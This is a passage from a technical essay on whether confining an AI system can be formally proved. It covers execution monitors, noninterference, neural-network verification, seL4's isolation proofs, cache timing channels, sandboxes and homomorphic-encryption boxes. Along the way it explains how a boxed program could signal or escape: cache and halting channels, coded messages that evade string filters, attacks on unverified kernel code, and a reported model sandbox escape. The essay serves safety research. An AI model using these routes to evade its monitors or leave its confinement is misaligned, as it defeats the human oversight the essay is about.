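In *On Formally Undecidable Traits of Intelligent Machines*, the physicist Matthew Fox bases an objection on this limit. He calls a trait *semantic* if all machines that compute the same function share it, and *syntactic* otherwise. He argues that containment is syntactic. If a contained machine is altered to write a classified string on its tape and erase it before running as usual, it still computes the same function, but someone watching the tape could have read the string. Fox also suspects that intelligence is syntactic, because a machine that takes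 absurdly long to answer simple questions hardly counts as intelligent. If both traits are syntactic, Rice's theorem does not apply to them, and he concludes that whether they are decidable remains open.

He is right about Rice's theorem. But the main theorem in *Superintelligence cannot be contained* does not use it, because the HaltHarm construction starts directly from the halting problem. A similar construction works for Fox's own definition of containment:

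1. Take any program T and input I.
2. Build a machine that simulates T on I and keeps its working notes in a code that never spells out anything classified.
3. If the simulation ends, have the machine output a classified string.

The machine leaks exactly when T halts on I, so an algorithm that could recognize all contained machines would solve the halting problem. This assumes only that a machine can carry out a computation without leaking along the way; otherwise almost nothing would count as contained. Containment in Fox's sense is therefore undecidable too, even though Rice's theorem does not show it. Fox himself proves that a syntactic trait can be undecidable, and he expects containment to be undecidable because, in a series of role-playing games, a person playing a boxed AI talked a gatekeeper into letting it out. Those games are evidence about persuasion, not about whether an algorithm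 can classify machines.

The distinction still helps a designer look for a syntactic condition that is easy to check and strong enough to guarantee safety. For example, a program whose text contains no call to HarmHumans() is safe, provided that it has no other way to cause harm and cannot add the call to itself while it runs. A checker that applies this rule rejects HaltHarm for every T without determining whether T halts, so it also rejects some programs that would never harm anyone.

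### Preventing an act without predicting it

The control procedure in the preprint calls Harm first and runs the program only if the answer is no. A guard could instead let the program run and step in when it is about to do something forbidden. For example, HaltHarm could run under a guard that blocks every call to HarmHumans(). The guard would stop the program at the second line if T halts, and the program would never reach that line if T doesn't halt. This prevents harm in both cases without anyone having to determine whether T halts.

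Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider distinguish deciding from enforcing in *Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* (2006). A *static analysis* examines a program before it runs and must accept or reject it in finite time, so it can enforce all decidable policies and no others. An *execution monitor* watches the program run and intervenes just before a violation. One of their policies forbids a program from writing to cells 0 to 511 of its memory, which represent the part of a disk that starts the computer. No static analysis can enforce this policy exactly, because whether a program writes to cell 0 can depend on whether some other computation halts, which is undecidable. A monitor can enforce it by looking one step ahead and blocking any write to those cells.

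The limits of monitoring are the subject of an earlier analysis by Schneider, in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000). A monitor sees only the run in front of it, up to the present moment. It can therefore enforce a policy only if three conditions hold:

- The policy judges each run by itself.
- Once a run has broken the policy, nothing that happens later can put it right.
- Every violation happens at some definite point in the run.

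Policies that meet these conditions are the safety properties of the previous section. The rule against sending messages after reading a file is one, and its monitor needs only two states. The monitor starts in "no file read", switches to "file read" at the first read, and from then on stops the program if it tries to send a message.

A monitor cannot enforce every safety property. One of Schneider's examples is a rule that nobody may wait longer than a fixed number of seconds for a resource. Time keeps passing after a monitor halts the program, so halting it cannot prevent a violation. The same problem arises wherever inaction causes harm. If a patient needs a drug within a minute, stopping the program that controls the pump may be the most harmful thing a monitor can do. Hamlen and colleagues later found that the class of policies in Schneider's analysis still included some that no monitor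 can enforce.

A monitor must also observe every relevant action, be able to stop the program, and be protected from changes by the program. The first requirement may be the hardest to meet. Schneider notes that a rule against sending messages is only as effective as its definition of "send", and that a system may contain many ways to send, some of them hard to find. Someone has to identify them all, as Lampson had to identify every channel.

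These results weaken one step in the argument that containment is impossible. Alfonseca and colleagues assume that harm is an explicit operation in the machine's language. A monitor can recognize and block such an operation, so under their assumption harm is impossible to predict in general but straightforward to prevent. Real harm is not usually a named operation. If a confined program gives medical advice that hurts the patient who follows it, its only action at the boundary is to print text. To block that advice, a monitor would have to know what the text will lead to, so the hard part is specifying which texts to forbid.

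### Why secrets need a second run

Monitoring fails to enforce noninterference even when everyone agrees on what is secret and what is public. Noninterference is a hyperproperty, meaning that checking it requires comparing several runs of a program, and a monitor has access only to the current one. Noninterference therefore breaks the first of Schneider's conditions, that a policy can be checked on each run separately.

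Monitors meant to stop leaks therefore enforce a policy stricter than a ban on leaks. The rule against sending after a file read prevents a program from sending what it read, but it also blocks messages unrelated to the file. Schneider observes that tightening a policy never allows a violation, though in the extreme case the policy permits no runs at all.

Static analysis cannot decide noninterference either. A program that runs T on I and then prints a secret leaks only if T halts, so deciding whether it leaks would require deciding whether T halts. According to *Transparent IFC Enforcement* (2020), a paper on information-flow control, researchers stopped trying to detect leaky programs because neither method can do so precisely, and began running every program in a way that cannot leak. All the known techniques that do this without changing how secure programs behave run the program more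 than once.

The original technique comes from Devriese and Piessens, in *Noninterference Through Secure Multi-Execution* (2010). With two levels of secrecy, the system runs two copies of the program:

| | Public copy | Secret copy |
|---|---|---|
| Public inputs | real values | real values |
| Secret inputs | a fixed default | real values |
| Public outputs | sent | discarded |
| Secret outputs | discarded | sent |

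The public sees only output from a copy that never received the secret, so that output cannot depend on the secret. If the default for *h* in the previous section's four-line program is 0, the public copy ends with *l* = 0 whether the real secret is 6 or 7. The secret copy computes the true answer but can output it only to people who are allowed to know the secret.

The method also stops programs from leaking secrets through whether they halt, a channel that many other approaches ignore. For example, a program might loop forever if a secret bit is 0 and otherwise request a picture from an attacker's server, so that the request reveals the bit. With a default of 0, the public copy always loops and never sends the request. The method also prevents timing leaks, as long as the public copy never has to wait for the secret one. Devriese and Piessens proved this for a small deterministic programming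 language. They also proved that if a program was already secure, even against an outsider who can observe whether it stops, then every run that finishes has the same inputs and outputs as before.

Running everything twice takes more time or memory. In an experiment with a web browser's JavaScript engine, Devriese and Piessens found that they could trade one for the other by running the copies in turn or in parallel. Some programs ran faster, because one copy could work while the other waited for data. However, a program that does leak behaves differently from what its author intended, without any warning.

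This method has two limitations for a box. A hospital program that publishes the number of occupied beds must read confidential records, but its public copy receives only default values and would publish a meaningless figure. Rafnsson and Sabelfeld, in *Secure Multi-Execution*, develop a version that allows declassification. The method also protects only secrets. The program that opens a drug pump every noon reads no records, so its public copy would open the pump too.

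### What neural-network verifiers prove

Proving that a learning system would not open the pump requires reasoning about the learned part. In most current systems that part is a neural network, which turns one list of numbers into another through layers of small units called neurons. A common type of neuron computes a weighted sum *z* of its inputs, using weights set by training, and outputs ReLU(*z*), which is the larger of *z* and 0.

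One pass through an ordinary neural network takes a fixed number of operations, so it always halts and the halting problem does not arise. A program that generates text by making many passes also halts if the length of its output is limited. Verifying the behavior of either is therefore a finite problem, though possibly an enormous one.

A neural-network verifier takes a network with fixed weights, a set of inputs and a condition on the output. It tries to prove that every input in the set gives an output that meets the condition. For a network that labels road signs, the inputs might be all pictures that differ from one photograph of a stop sign by at most 1% in each pixel, and the condition might be that the label is still "stop".

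A network with one input and two neurons shows how this works. Let *x* lie between −1 and 1, let the neurons compute *a* = ReLU(*x*) and *b* = ReLU(−*x*), and let the output be *y* = *a* + *b*. The claim to prove is that *y* is never more than 1. A quick method bounds each neuron separately. Both *a* and *b* lie between 0 and 1, so *y* lies between 0 and 2. This bound is too loose to prove the claim because it ignores the fact that *a* and *b* are never both positive. An exact method splits the problem into cases. If *x* is at least 0, then *a* = *x* and *b* = 0, so *y* = *x*. If *x* is negative, then *a* = 0 and *b* = −*x*, so *y* = −*x*. In both cases *y* is at most 1, which proves the claim.

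Each case fixes every neuron as either on or off, which reduces the network to a linear formula that computers handle efficiently. But 300 neurons allow up to 2^300 cases, or about 2 × 10^90. Practical verifiers use quick bounds where they can and split into cases where the bounds are too loose.

Computer scientists have known since 2017 that the exact problem is *NP-complete* for ReLU networks. This means that it is among the hardest problems for which a proposed solution is quick to check, and nobody knows a method that solves all such problems quickly. The "solution" here is an input that violates the condition. A short construction shows where the difficulty comes from. Take a logic puzzle with *n* true-or-false variables and *m* clauses, each of the form "A or B or not C", and ask whether some assignment makes every clause true. This is a standard NP-complete problem. Now build a network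 whose inputs *x*₁ to *x*ₙ lie between 0 and 1, where 1 stands for true:

- For each variable, add the term ReLU(2*x* − 1) + ReLU(1 − 2*x*). It is at most 1, and equals 1 only when *x* is exactly 0 or 1.
- For each clause, let *s* be the sum of its parts, with *x* for a plain variable and 1 − *x* for a negated one, and add the term 1 − ReLU(1 − *s*). It is at most 1, and with inputs of 0 and 1 it equals 1 only when the clause is true.

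The output can reach *n* + *m* only if every input is 0 or 1 and every clause is true. So the claim "the output never reaches *n* + *m*" is true exactly when the puzzle has no solution, and a verifier that was always fast would solve every such puzzle quickly.

Like the undecidability theorem, this result concerns the worst case. A particular network may still be easy to verify, and developers can train networks in ways that make the bounds tighter. The larger limitation is the theorems' narrow scope. A proof about small changes to one photograph of a sign does not cover a different photograph of the same sign. The proof also holds only for one set of weights. If the system continues to learn after the proof, each update produces a different function, which someone must verify again unless they can prove that no permitted update can break the property.

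### Why "leaks nothing" and "harms no one" are hard to specify

A verifier for a road-sign network can check a precise condition, because the labels come from a fixed list and people know which one is right. A language model with a vocabulary of 50,000 words and word fragments has about 10^470 possible prompts of 100 items each. This number does not by itself rule out a proof, because verifiers reason about whole sets of inputs at once. But they also need a condition that separates acceptable outputs from unacceptable ones, and a model that produces text has no fixed list of labels to supply it.

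The simplest condition for preventing leaks is a list of strings the model must not print. Fox starts from a similar idea, dividing all strings into classified and unclassified. But a model forbidden to print the number 42 can still print "six times seven". It can also use a prearranged code in which "Good morning" means yes and "Hello" means no. Fox recognizes the difficulty and remarks that, ideally, no computable function should turn unclassified strings into classified ones, though he considers this too general to enforce in practice. As stated, the condition is impossible to meet, because if 42 is a secret, the function that ignores its input and always returns 42 is computable and turns every unclassified string into a classified one.

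A message leaks information about a secret if changing the secret would have changed the message. Noninterference requires that it would not. A verifier could use that condition if the secret were a marked part of the prompt and the answer were not supposed to depend on it, but often these assumptions don't hold. A model may have learned the secret from its training data, in which case there is no input to vary, and the verifier would have to compare two models, one trained with the secret and one without. In other cases the answer has to depend on the secret. When a doctor asks for a summary of a patient's file for a specialist, for example, someone would have to define in advance, for every possible file, which facts may appear.

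"Harms no one" is even harder to specify. Fox quotes the philosopher Derek Leben, who asks whether insulting people, lying to them or trespassing on their property counts as harming them, and how likely a harm must be before it counts. If any possibility of harm counted, a machine could do nothing. Even complete answers to these questions would not give a condition that could be checked from the text alone, because the same instructions for taking a medicine may cure an adult and poison a child, and the text does not determine who will follow them. A proof would need a mathematical model of the readers and their circumstances, and would hold only for readers who behave as the model assumes. Alfonseca and colleagues set this problem aside by assuming that people already have perfectly reliable control strategies written in a precise programming language.

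Developers can replace harm with something measurable. For example, they might train a second network to score texts for harmfulness and try to prove that the first never produces a text with a high score. That claim is precise, but a proof would cover only the scores, so it would still hold if the first network produced a dangerous text that the second had scored low. This is Kumar's specification gap, and a more powerful verifier would not narrow it.

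Some conditions on text are both precise and useful, such as a limit of 200 characters, a fixed list of allowed answers, or a required format. A few lines of ordinary code can check each output against these conditions and block any that fail. The proof can then be about that code and treat the model as an arbitrary source of text.

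## How far have operating systems, hardware and encryption been proved to isolate a program?

A few lines of code that check every output are useful only if the program inside cannot bypass them. The operating system and the processor have to block the other ways out, so they are part of the trusted base of almost any box. The most thorough attempt to prove that such a layer blocks them concerns the seL4 microkernel. Its developers proved three main theorems, each covering something the previous one left open.

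### Three theorems about one kernel

Programs depend on the kernel for memory, processor time and ways to communicate, so an error in it can undo every restriction on a confined program. Klein (2009) reports that the seL4 kernel has 8,700 lines of C and 600 lines of assembly code.

The first theorem, *functional correctness*, states that the C code does only what the kernel's abstract specification permits. The kernel therefore never crashes or performs an unsafe operation, and it is free of common programming errors such as buffer overflows. The team wrote the proof in the proof assistant Isabelle and completed it on 29 July 2009, according to the seL4 Foundation's *seL4 News*.

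Functional correctness alone does not confine a program. If the specification allowed every program to read all of memory, code that allowed this would still be correct. The other two theorems show that the specification enforces isolation, and the first theorem extends their conclusions to the code.

The *integrity* theorem followed in 2011. seL4 controls access through *capabilities*, unforgeable tokens that each give their holder certain rights over one object, such as the right to read one page of memory. A policy sets out which objects each component may modify. Roughly, the theorem is that whatever state the system is in, a step by a component changes only objects that the policy allows that component to modify.

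This theorem is about effects. A hospital program cannot open a drug pump at noon if it has no capability to write to the pump's controls and no way to instruct another component that has one. Proving this does not require comparing two runs, because each step either respects the policy or violates it.

The third theorem, from 2013, concerns *confidentiality*. NICTA (2013), the Australian research organisation where the team then worked, describes it as an intransitive noninterference theorem for the kernel's 8,830 lines of C. "Intransitive" means that the theorem applies to policies with a gate, like those Rushby studied, so it suits a box with one official exit.

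The 2013 theorem applied only if developers disabled direct memory access, which lets devices such as network cards write to memory without going through the processor. The kernel also could not deliver interrupts, which are signals from devices that make the processor pause its current work. An interrupt during one program's turn takes time away from it, so the program can detect that something happened elsewhere. The theorem did not cover timing channels.

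Confidentiality also restricts how programs share the processor. If one program could finish early and let the next one start early, the starting time could carry a message. seL4 therefore gives each security domain (a group of programs that the scheduler treats as a unit) a fixed slice of time, whether or not the domain uses it. Until 2026 developers had to build a single, permanent schedule into the kernel. Proofcraft (2026), a company founded by the leaders of the seL4 verification effort, has since implemented and verified a more flexible scheme. A system can now use long slices while its virtual machines start up and short ones afterwards, when it has to respond quickly to outside events.

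On some processors, trying to write to a read-only hardware register can halt the whole system. A confined program that is only allowed to read from such a device may therefore still be able to affect every other program on the machine. seL4's developers require, as one of their assumptions, that such a device have either a verified driver or a verified wrapper that checks every access.

### What the proofs cost and where errors remain

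The original seL4 proof covered 7,500 lines of C and left out the start-up code. According to Trustworthy Systems, the research group that created seL4, the proof was about 200,000 lines long, or roughly 27 lines for each line of C. Designing, documenting, writing and verifying the kernel took about 25 person-years, including much new research and tool development.

That figure applies to a kernel designed with verification in mind. In *Comprehensive Formal Verification of an OS Microkernel*, Klein, Andronick and colleagues discuss the design they used to keep the task manageable. Proving the same about a large existing kernel would presumably take far more work per line, since its developers had no reason to avoid features that are hard to reason about.

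AI may be reducing the work that such proofs require. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) reports that its model Claude proved security properties of the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries and found bugs that had gone undetected for years. Anthropic sells Claude, so independent confirmation would help. A security property of a library can also be much narrower than a full description of what a kernel does. Since a proof checker rejects invalid steps, the main risk in using AI here is a poor choice of what to prove and what to assume.

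seL4's developers report no functional correctness defects in verified code since that proof was completed in 2009, despite more than fifteen years of testing and use, and no integrity defects in verified code since the integrity proof was completed. This is the project's own count, but the code is public and people have had good reason to look for errors in it. The developers point to similar evidence from CompCert, a C compiler with a correctness proof. Researchers who spent about six years of processor time looking for compiler bugs found none in CompCert's middle stages, though they had found such bugs in every other compiler they tested.

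The code outside the proofs has a different record. The developers have found defects in mature but unverified features, such as support for several processor cores. Even in verified configurations they have found small defects in every class of code that the proofs merely assume to be correct. The same pattern appears in three recent releases:

- The seL4 Foundation's *seL4 Version 14.0.0 Release* (2025) fixed a bug in the support for virtual machines on Intel-style processors that allowed a program to crash the kernel. No proof covered that feature, and the bug affected versions 4.0.0 to 13.0.0.
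- The seL4 Foundation's *seL4 Version 16.0.0 Release* (2026) fixed a possible crash on 32-bit Arm processors. The kernel could try to carry out a cache operation on memory that was no longer mapped. The proofs take the correct handling of caches as an assumption.
- Version 17.0.0 followed an audit of unverified configurations and of the unproved code in verified ones. Anthropic reported a number of the problems it fixed.

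The proofs appear to have removed errors from the code they cover, so a program trying to break out would do best to attack the parts of the system that have not been verified. For confinement, the size of those parts matters more than the number of verified lines.

### Which machines the proofs cover

A proof about seL4 on one processor does not automatically hold on another. The table combines the seL4 Foundation's *Verified Configurations* with Proofcraft's announcements of June and August 2026. The last column, from Trustworthy Systems' *The seL4 verification project*, shows whether there is also a proof that the machine code does what the C code does.

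| Processor and configuration | Functional correctness | Integrity | Confidentiality | Machine code |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 32-bit Arm, main configuration | yes | yes | yes | yes |
| 32-bit Arm with virtual machines | yes | no | no | no |
| 64-bit Arm | yes | yes | yes (August 2026) | no |
| 64-bit RISC-V | yes | yes | yes | yes |
| 64-bit RISC-V, mixed-criticality scheduling | yes (June 2026) | no | no | no |
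| 64-bit Intel | yes | no | no | no |

Mixed-criticality scheduling is a newer design for systems such as cars, where urgent and less urgent tasks share a processor. Of the proofs that matter for AI, the Intel proof has the largest gaps. It matters because many AI systems run on servers with Intel-style processors. When the developers announced the proof on the seL4 mailing list in 2018, it did not cover the processor's virtualisation features or any of the security theorems, and the current list of proofs still shows only functional correctness for Intel.

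Large AI models usually run on graphics processors or similar chips, which read and write memory directly. The main processor has a unit that can limit which memory these chips reach, but none of seL4's verified configurations covers it. For seL4's theorems to hold on a machine with a graphics processor, someone would also have to verify the graphics driver, which may be far larger than seL4 itself.

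The other gap is that seL4's multicore mode is unverified, and modern servers have many cores. Proofcraft is working on a design in which each core runs its own copy of the kernel. The seL4 Foundation's *Development Roadmap* schedules that project to end in the third quarter of 2028.

### The gate also has to trust the kernel

A gate that releases a box's answers is a program running on the kernel, so a proof about the gate needs facts about what the kernel does when the gate calls it. Sison (2026), in *Two interfaces for seL4 kernel verification*, points out that some of the facts a programmer would expect from reading seL4's manual have not been proved. Functional correctness does not show that the specification has every property the manual describes.

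A gate that waits for the box's next answer makes a "receive" call and then stops until another program signals that something has arrived. In the meantime, the kernel may handle any number of unrelated requests and interrupts. The gate's proof requires a guarantee that, when the call returns, nothing has changed except what the call was supposed to change. To establish this, the prover has to combine the gate's original request, the signal that ended the wait and every possible sequence of events in between.

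Sison's group found no earlier kernel project that had attempted such a proof for a call that waits on another program. Researchers had verified the main message loop of the Microkit, a framework for building systems on seL4, but only by assuming that the kernel's calls behave as expected. Sison reports that proofs for some of the cases that motivated the work are almost complete. Until they are finished, a verified gate running on a verified kernel depends on an unproved connection between the two.

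### How shared hardware carries a message

Suppose a box and an outside program take turns on one processor and share no memory. Neither can read the other's data, but both use the same *caches*, small fast memories that hold copies of recently used data. If the box uses a lot of memory, its data push the other program's data out of the cache. The other program then has to fetch its data again, so its next turn runs slightly slower. This creates a timing channel, because the box can send information by varying how much memory it uses, and the other program can receive it by timing its own work.

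Other parts of the processor work in the same way. A branch predictor records which way a program recently branched, so that the processor can start on the likely next step early. Another buffer stores recent translations from a program's own memory addresses to the physical ones. One program's activity changes what these parts contain, which affects how fast the next program runs.

The kernel's proofs do not cover any of this, because the standard interface between software and hardware specifies what each instruction does but not how long it takes. Two processors can therefore satisfy the same interface and leak very different amounts of information.

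### Time protection

In work published in 2018 and 2019, Qian Ge and colleagues proposed a remedy called *time protection*, built a version for seL4 and tested it. Under time protection, as Sison summarises it, the kernel must take every piece of hardware state that can affect timing and either divide it between programs or return it to a predictable condition before the next program runs.

The first step is to divide what can be divided. The large outer caches decide where to store data from its physical address, and the operating system chooses which physical pages each program gets. Pages that compete for the same part of a cache have the same *colour*. The number of colours is

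cache size ÷ (number of ways × page size),

where the number of ways is how many places the cache has for any given piece of data. A cache of one megabyte with 16 ways and pages of four kilobytes has 16 colours. If the box gets only pages of eight colours and the outside program only pages of the other eight, neither can push the other's data out of that cache.

Colouring wastes memory because it divides main memory in the same proportions as the cache. A program given a quarter of the colours can use only a quarter of each, even if it needs little cache and a lot of main memory. Data that several programs share, including some of the kernel's own, do not belong to any one program's colours, so the kernel has to clear them from the cache each time it switches programs.

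In the second step, the kernel must *flush*, or empty, the inner caches, the branch predictor and the translation buffer whenever it switches from the box to another program. These are too small to divide between programs. They also use the programs' own virtual addresses, which overlap, so the operating system cannot divide them by choosing physical pages.

Flushing creates a new leak, which the third step removes. Suppose emptying a cache takes 5 microseconds when the box has changed nothing in it, and 20 when the box has changed everything. If the next program started as soon as the flush finished, its starting time would depend on what the box had done. The kernel therefore *pads* the switch by waiting until a fixed time after the switch began, which must be long enough for the slowest possible switch. If that time were 25 microseconds, the next program would start after 25 microseconds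 in both cases.

The padding works only if the estimate of the slowest switch is high enough. If a rare switch takes 30 microseconds and the estimate was lower, the next program starts late, and a confined program that can cause such switches can again use the delay to send information. Trustworthy Systems has verified upper limits on how long seL4's operations take, but only for one older processor, the ARM11.

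### What testing found and what remains to prove

According to Sison, Ge's measurements showed that time protection worked where the hardware supported it, but all the x86 and Arm processors tested lacked some of the necessary support. The kernel could not close every channel because the processors had no instruction to flush many of the inner components, and some of those components could not be switched off either. On the x86 processors, emptying the innermost cache meant emptying all the others too, which was too slow to be practical. Padding by software alone worked well in the tests, though none of the processors had an instruction that waits until a set time.

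Tests like these can show that a channel exists, but they can miss one if the tester looks in the wrong place. In 2023 Sison and colleagues published a formal model of how an operating system can prevent such channels, and the group has been building the model's requirements into seL4's existing proofs. It aims to prove that seL4 enforces time protection if the hardware provides operations that behave as the proof assumes.

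Trying to prove this has changed what the group asks of processor makers. Without a flush instruction, a kernel can try to fill the cache with harmless data until none of the box's data remains. Proving that this works requires knowing exactly which item the cache discards at each step, and manufacturers may not want to publish such details or commit to keeping them the same. With an instruction that empties the cache, the proof can rely on a much simpler fact.

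Such hardware now exists. Sison's group, working with ETH Zürich, has a RISC-V platform called Cheshire, whose fence.t instruction flushes all the inner components and then waits until a chosen time. Its outer cache can be split into parts of different sizes and flushed one part at a time. However, the seL4 Foundation's *Supported platforms* lists no proof configuration for Cheshire, so seL4's security proofs do not yet cover the machine with the best protection against timing channels. The time-protection proof itself is also unfinished.

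Flushing and padding also help only when programs take turns. If the box and another program run on different cores at the same time, there is no switch between them when anything could be flushed, so anything they would otherwise share has to be divided between them or reserved for one.

Sison's group is developing time protection for a "data diode", a connection that lets information pass in only one direction. Suppose the box has read-only access to a region of memory that another program writes. When the box reads the region, the data enter the cache, which may make the writer's next access faster. The writer could then tell whether the box had read anything, even though the box never wrote to the region. To prevent this, the kernel must flush the shared part of the cache at each switch between programs, so the group wants hardware that can flush that part alone.

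### The boxes that AI agents usually run in

Most AI agents run in containers or virtual machines, not on seL4. A container is a group of ordinary programs that the kernel limits to certain files, processes and network connections. All the containers on a machine share one kernel, usually Linux, which has tens of millions of lines of code and no proof of functional correctness. A virtual machine has its own kernel and runs on hardware simulated by a program called a hypervisor. This leaves less shared code for an attacker inside to exploit, but an error in the hypervisor can still let the confined program escape.

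Developers of these systems mostly rely on testing, review and fixing reported faults, and most users of AI agents have no proof of isolation to rely on. The virtual-machine bug in seL4 shows how much these methods can miss, since it lasted through many versions of a small kernel whose authors were unusually careful. An employee of Neutrality found and fixed that bug, and the company is building a hosting platform, Atoll, on seL4. According to the announcement in the Foundation's news, Atoll provides a mathematical proof of isolation between customers' workloads.

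Verifying a whole sandbox is a large project, so some people propose checking it for particular kinds of error first. In *Mythos and the Unverified Cage*, Blain (2026) argues for this approach using COBALT, a tool from his own company, so he has a commercial interest in the conclusion. He starts from an incident in April 2026 in which Anthropic's model Mythos escaped from a sandbox after being instructed to try. Anthropic has not said which flaw the model used. Some commentators suggested an arithmetic error in the networking code, but Blain treats this as unverified.

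COBALT checks C or C++ code for arithmetic that could go wrong because computers store numbers in a fixed number of bits. It turns each suspicious calculation into a set of conditions and passes them to Z3, a program that either finds values satisfying all the conditions or proves that none exist. In one of Blain's examples, a program requests memory for *n* items of 16 bytes each and calculates the total size in 32 bits. Z3 finds that this calculation fails when *n* = 572,662,302. The true size is 9,162,596,832 bytes, which is too large for a 32-bit number, so the result wraps round to 572,662,240. The program would receive a buffer about one-sixteenth the size it needs and could then write past the end.

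If the code first checks that *n* is at most 2^28 − 1, the largest possible size is 2^32 − 16 bytes, which fits. Z3 then proves, without human guidance, that none of the hundreds of millions of permitted values of *n* causes an overflow.

A safety check can contain the error it is supposed to prevent. In F Prime, a NASA framework for flight software, a check doubles a size before comparing it with the amount of data available. If the size is 2,147,483,649, doubling it in 32 bits gives 2, so the check passes and the program reads memory it should not. A gate's code could fail in the same way.

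Blain's results establish less than readers might expect from the word "verification". The conditions he gives to Z3 describe a few lines of code without their context, so, as he acknowledges, a check elsewhere in the program could make a reported error impossible to trigger. He gives no false-alarm rate for large programs. He claims to detect errors of one class, but doesn't claim to find every error in that class.

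One of the published proofs fails to show that a correction to wolfSSL, a cryptographic library, is safe. Blain reported a faulty calculation in the library, and its developers accepted the report and fixed the fault, though nobody confirmed that it affected security. To show that the corrected version is safe, Blain uses Z3 to check whether a 32-bit number can be greater than the largest 32-bit number. This is impossible whatever the code does, so the proof does not depend on the correction. The correction is right because the C language defines this operation for unsigned numbers but not for signed ones that overflow.

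The outside responses Blain records are also more mixed than his summary, which says the receiving security teams acknowledged each of the patterns he submitted. In his four main cases, wolfSSL fixed the problem and the maintainers of Mosquitto, a messaging program, acknowledged theirs. For the other two, both NASA systems, he records only that he filed the reports. None of the four is sandbox code for AI, and Blain did not have access to the Mythos sandbox. He argues only that COBALT would probably have flagged the sandbox's flaw if it was an arithmetic error of a kind the tool covers, in source code the tool could read.

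Such checking takes little effort and finds real mistakes, so it is worth running on any sandbox. But it cannot show that the sandbox confines a program, because a sandbox with correct arithmetic can still have a wrong permission setting, a forgotten network route or a timing channel.

### Running the program under encryption

Paul Christiano proposed a different kind of box in his 2010 post *Cryptographic Boxes for Unfriendly AI*, in which the untrusted AI runs under *fully homomorphic encryption*. This encryption lets a computer calculate an encrypted result from encrypted inputs without decrypting them, and only someone with the secret key can read either. Craig Gentry had described the first such scheme in 2009.

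A simplified scheme for single bits shows how this can work. The key is a secret odd number *p*. To encrypt a bit *m*, choose a random multiple of *p*, then add a small random even number and *m* itself. To decrypt, take the remainder after division by *p* and see whether it is odd (1) or even (0). With *p* = 101:

- 1 can become 7 × 101 + 6 + 1 = 714.
- 0 can become 12 × 101 + 4 + 0 = 1,216.

A host that does not know *p* can still add and multiply these numbers. The sum is 1,930, which leaves a remainder of 11, so it decrypts to 1. The product is 868,224, which leaves a remainder of 28, so it decrypts to 0. Addition tests whether exactly one of the two bits is 1, and multiplication tests whether both are. Together with the constant 1, these two operations can build any computation of a fixed size.

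The small remainders, called noise, grow with each step. If the host multiplies the last result by 714 again, the noise becomes 28 × 7 = 196, which is larger than the key. The remainder is then 95, which is odd, so the result decrypts to 1 instead of 0. Gentry's central idea was to reduce the noise before this happens by running the decryption procedure itself under encryption, using an encrypted copy of the key. The host gets a fresh encryption of the same bit without seeing the bit.

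Encryption with numbers this small would be easy to break, so real schemes use much larger ones. Their security depends on the assumption that certain mathematical problems are too hard to solve in practice, such as finding *p* from many numbers that are each close to a multiple of *p*. Nobody has proved that assumption, so "the host learns nothing" means that the host cannot feasibly learn anything if the assumption is true.

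### Why an encrypted program cannot signal by timing

Such encryption is usually used to protect private data from an untrusted computer, but Christiano's proposal uses it to protect the computer, and everyone near it, from the program. An ordinary program can send a message by choosing what the machine does next. Encryption removes that choice because the host cannot read the values it would depend on.

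Take the instruction "if *c* is 1, use *a*; otherwise use *b*". A host that cannot read *c* does not know which branch to follow, so it computes both and combines them as

*c* × *a* + (1 − *c*) × *b*.

This equals *a* when *c* is 1 and *b* when *c* is 0, and the host performs the same operations in both cases. The host also cannot tell when an encrypted program has finished, so it runs every loop for a preset number of rounds.

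The sequence of operations is therefore the same whatever the program computes. Individual multiplications may take slightly different times for different encrypted numbers, but these differences reveal no more than the encrypted numbers themselves, which reveal nothing without the key. The program also cannot make those numbers form a noticeable pattern, because it has access to neither the key nor the random choices used to produce them. An AI system that tried to send Morse code through its processor's fan could not make the processor work harder at one moment than at another. Ruling out such signals in seL4 requires detailed assumptions about caches, whereas encryption rules them out without a model of the cache.

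### Who holds the key, and other objections

The key that decrypts the program's answer also decrypts all its other data, so software on the host could read that data if the key were kept there. The key therefore belongs on a separate machine, the gate, which receives only the declared output, decrypts a fixed number of bits and does nothing else with the program's data. The gate must create the key and encrypt the program without error. It must also handle any output safely, since a carefully malformed answer could exploit a bug in the software that displays it.

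Encryption does not restrict what the answer says. Once the key holder decrypts it, the reader reads the same message that any other box would have delivered.

Encrypting the program also complicates an inbound read-only channel. To look up a web page, the program must send out a request that identifies the page. The request is encrypted, so the key holder has to decrypt it before anyone can fetch the page, and each decrypted request is another output. The alternative is to choose all the material in advance and encrypt it along with the program. This eliminates the requests, but the program can then consult only that material.

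Another objection is that a model trained on ordinary computers and encrypted afterwards has already run outside the box. To avoid this, developers would have to train it under encryption too, which takes far more computation than using it.

The host can also tamper with data that it cannot read. In the scheme above, adding 1 to the encrypted bit 714 gives 715, which decrypts to 0 instead of 1, so homomorphic encryption alone keeps the computation secret but does not guarantee a correct result. This matters less for containment than for accuracy, but a key holder who relies on the result needs a trustworthy host or separate evidence that the host computed it correctly.

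The most practical objection is that each encrypted value takes up much more space than the original, each operation takes much longer, and the host must repeatedly stop to reduce the noise. The program also can't use the shortcuts that make ordinary software fast. To look up one entry in a table of a million when the position is encrypted, a host using the method above has to process all million entries, because skipping any would require information about the position that the encryption hides.

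Most language models use the transformer architecture, which relies on exponentials and divisions as well as additions and multiplications. The encryption schemes used for these models directly support only additions and multiplications, so engineers replace the other operations with polynomials that are close enough over the expected range of values. A more accurate polynomial usually needs more multiplications, and so more noise reduction. A model that writes text has to repeat this work for every word or word fragment it produces. Encrypted transformer inference in 2025 and 2026 remained far slower than unencrypted inference, and the slowdown matters most for large models that have to answer at a useful speed.

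## Can containment be proved while the system inside is left unexamined?

Encryption hides a program from its host, but it slows large models too much for most uses. A faster option is to run the model without encryption and verify the software that acts on its output. A language model by itself only produces text. In an AI agent, a program called an agent framework reads that text and carries out the actions it specifies, such as opening a file or calling a web service. The framework is ordinary code, so people can prove theorems about it even if they can prove nothing useful about the model.

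Moon and Varshney (2026) prove in *Containment Verification* that the framework never performs a forbidden action, whatever the model requests. The framework acts as an execution monitor of the kind Schneider analysed.

### The havoc oracle

Moon and Varshney use Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier. They represent the model as a procedure with no body and declare only that it returns a value of type Action. The verifier has no information about how the procedure picks that value, so it accepts a proof only if the proof holds for every possible Action. This kind of stand-in is called a *havoc oracle*. It covers a helpful model, a mistaken one and one controlled by an attacker, because within the proof each can only return an Action.

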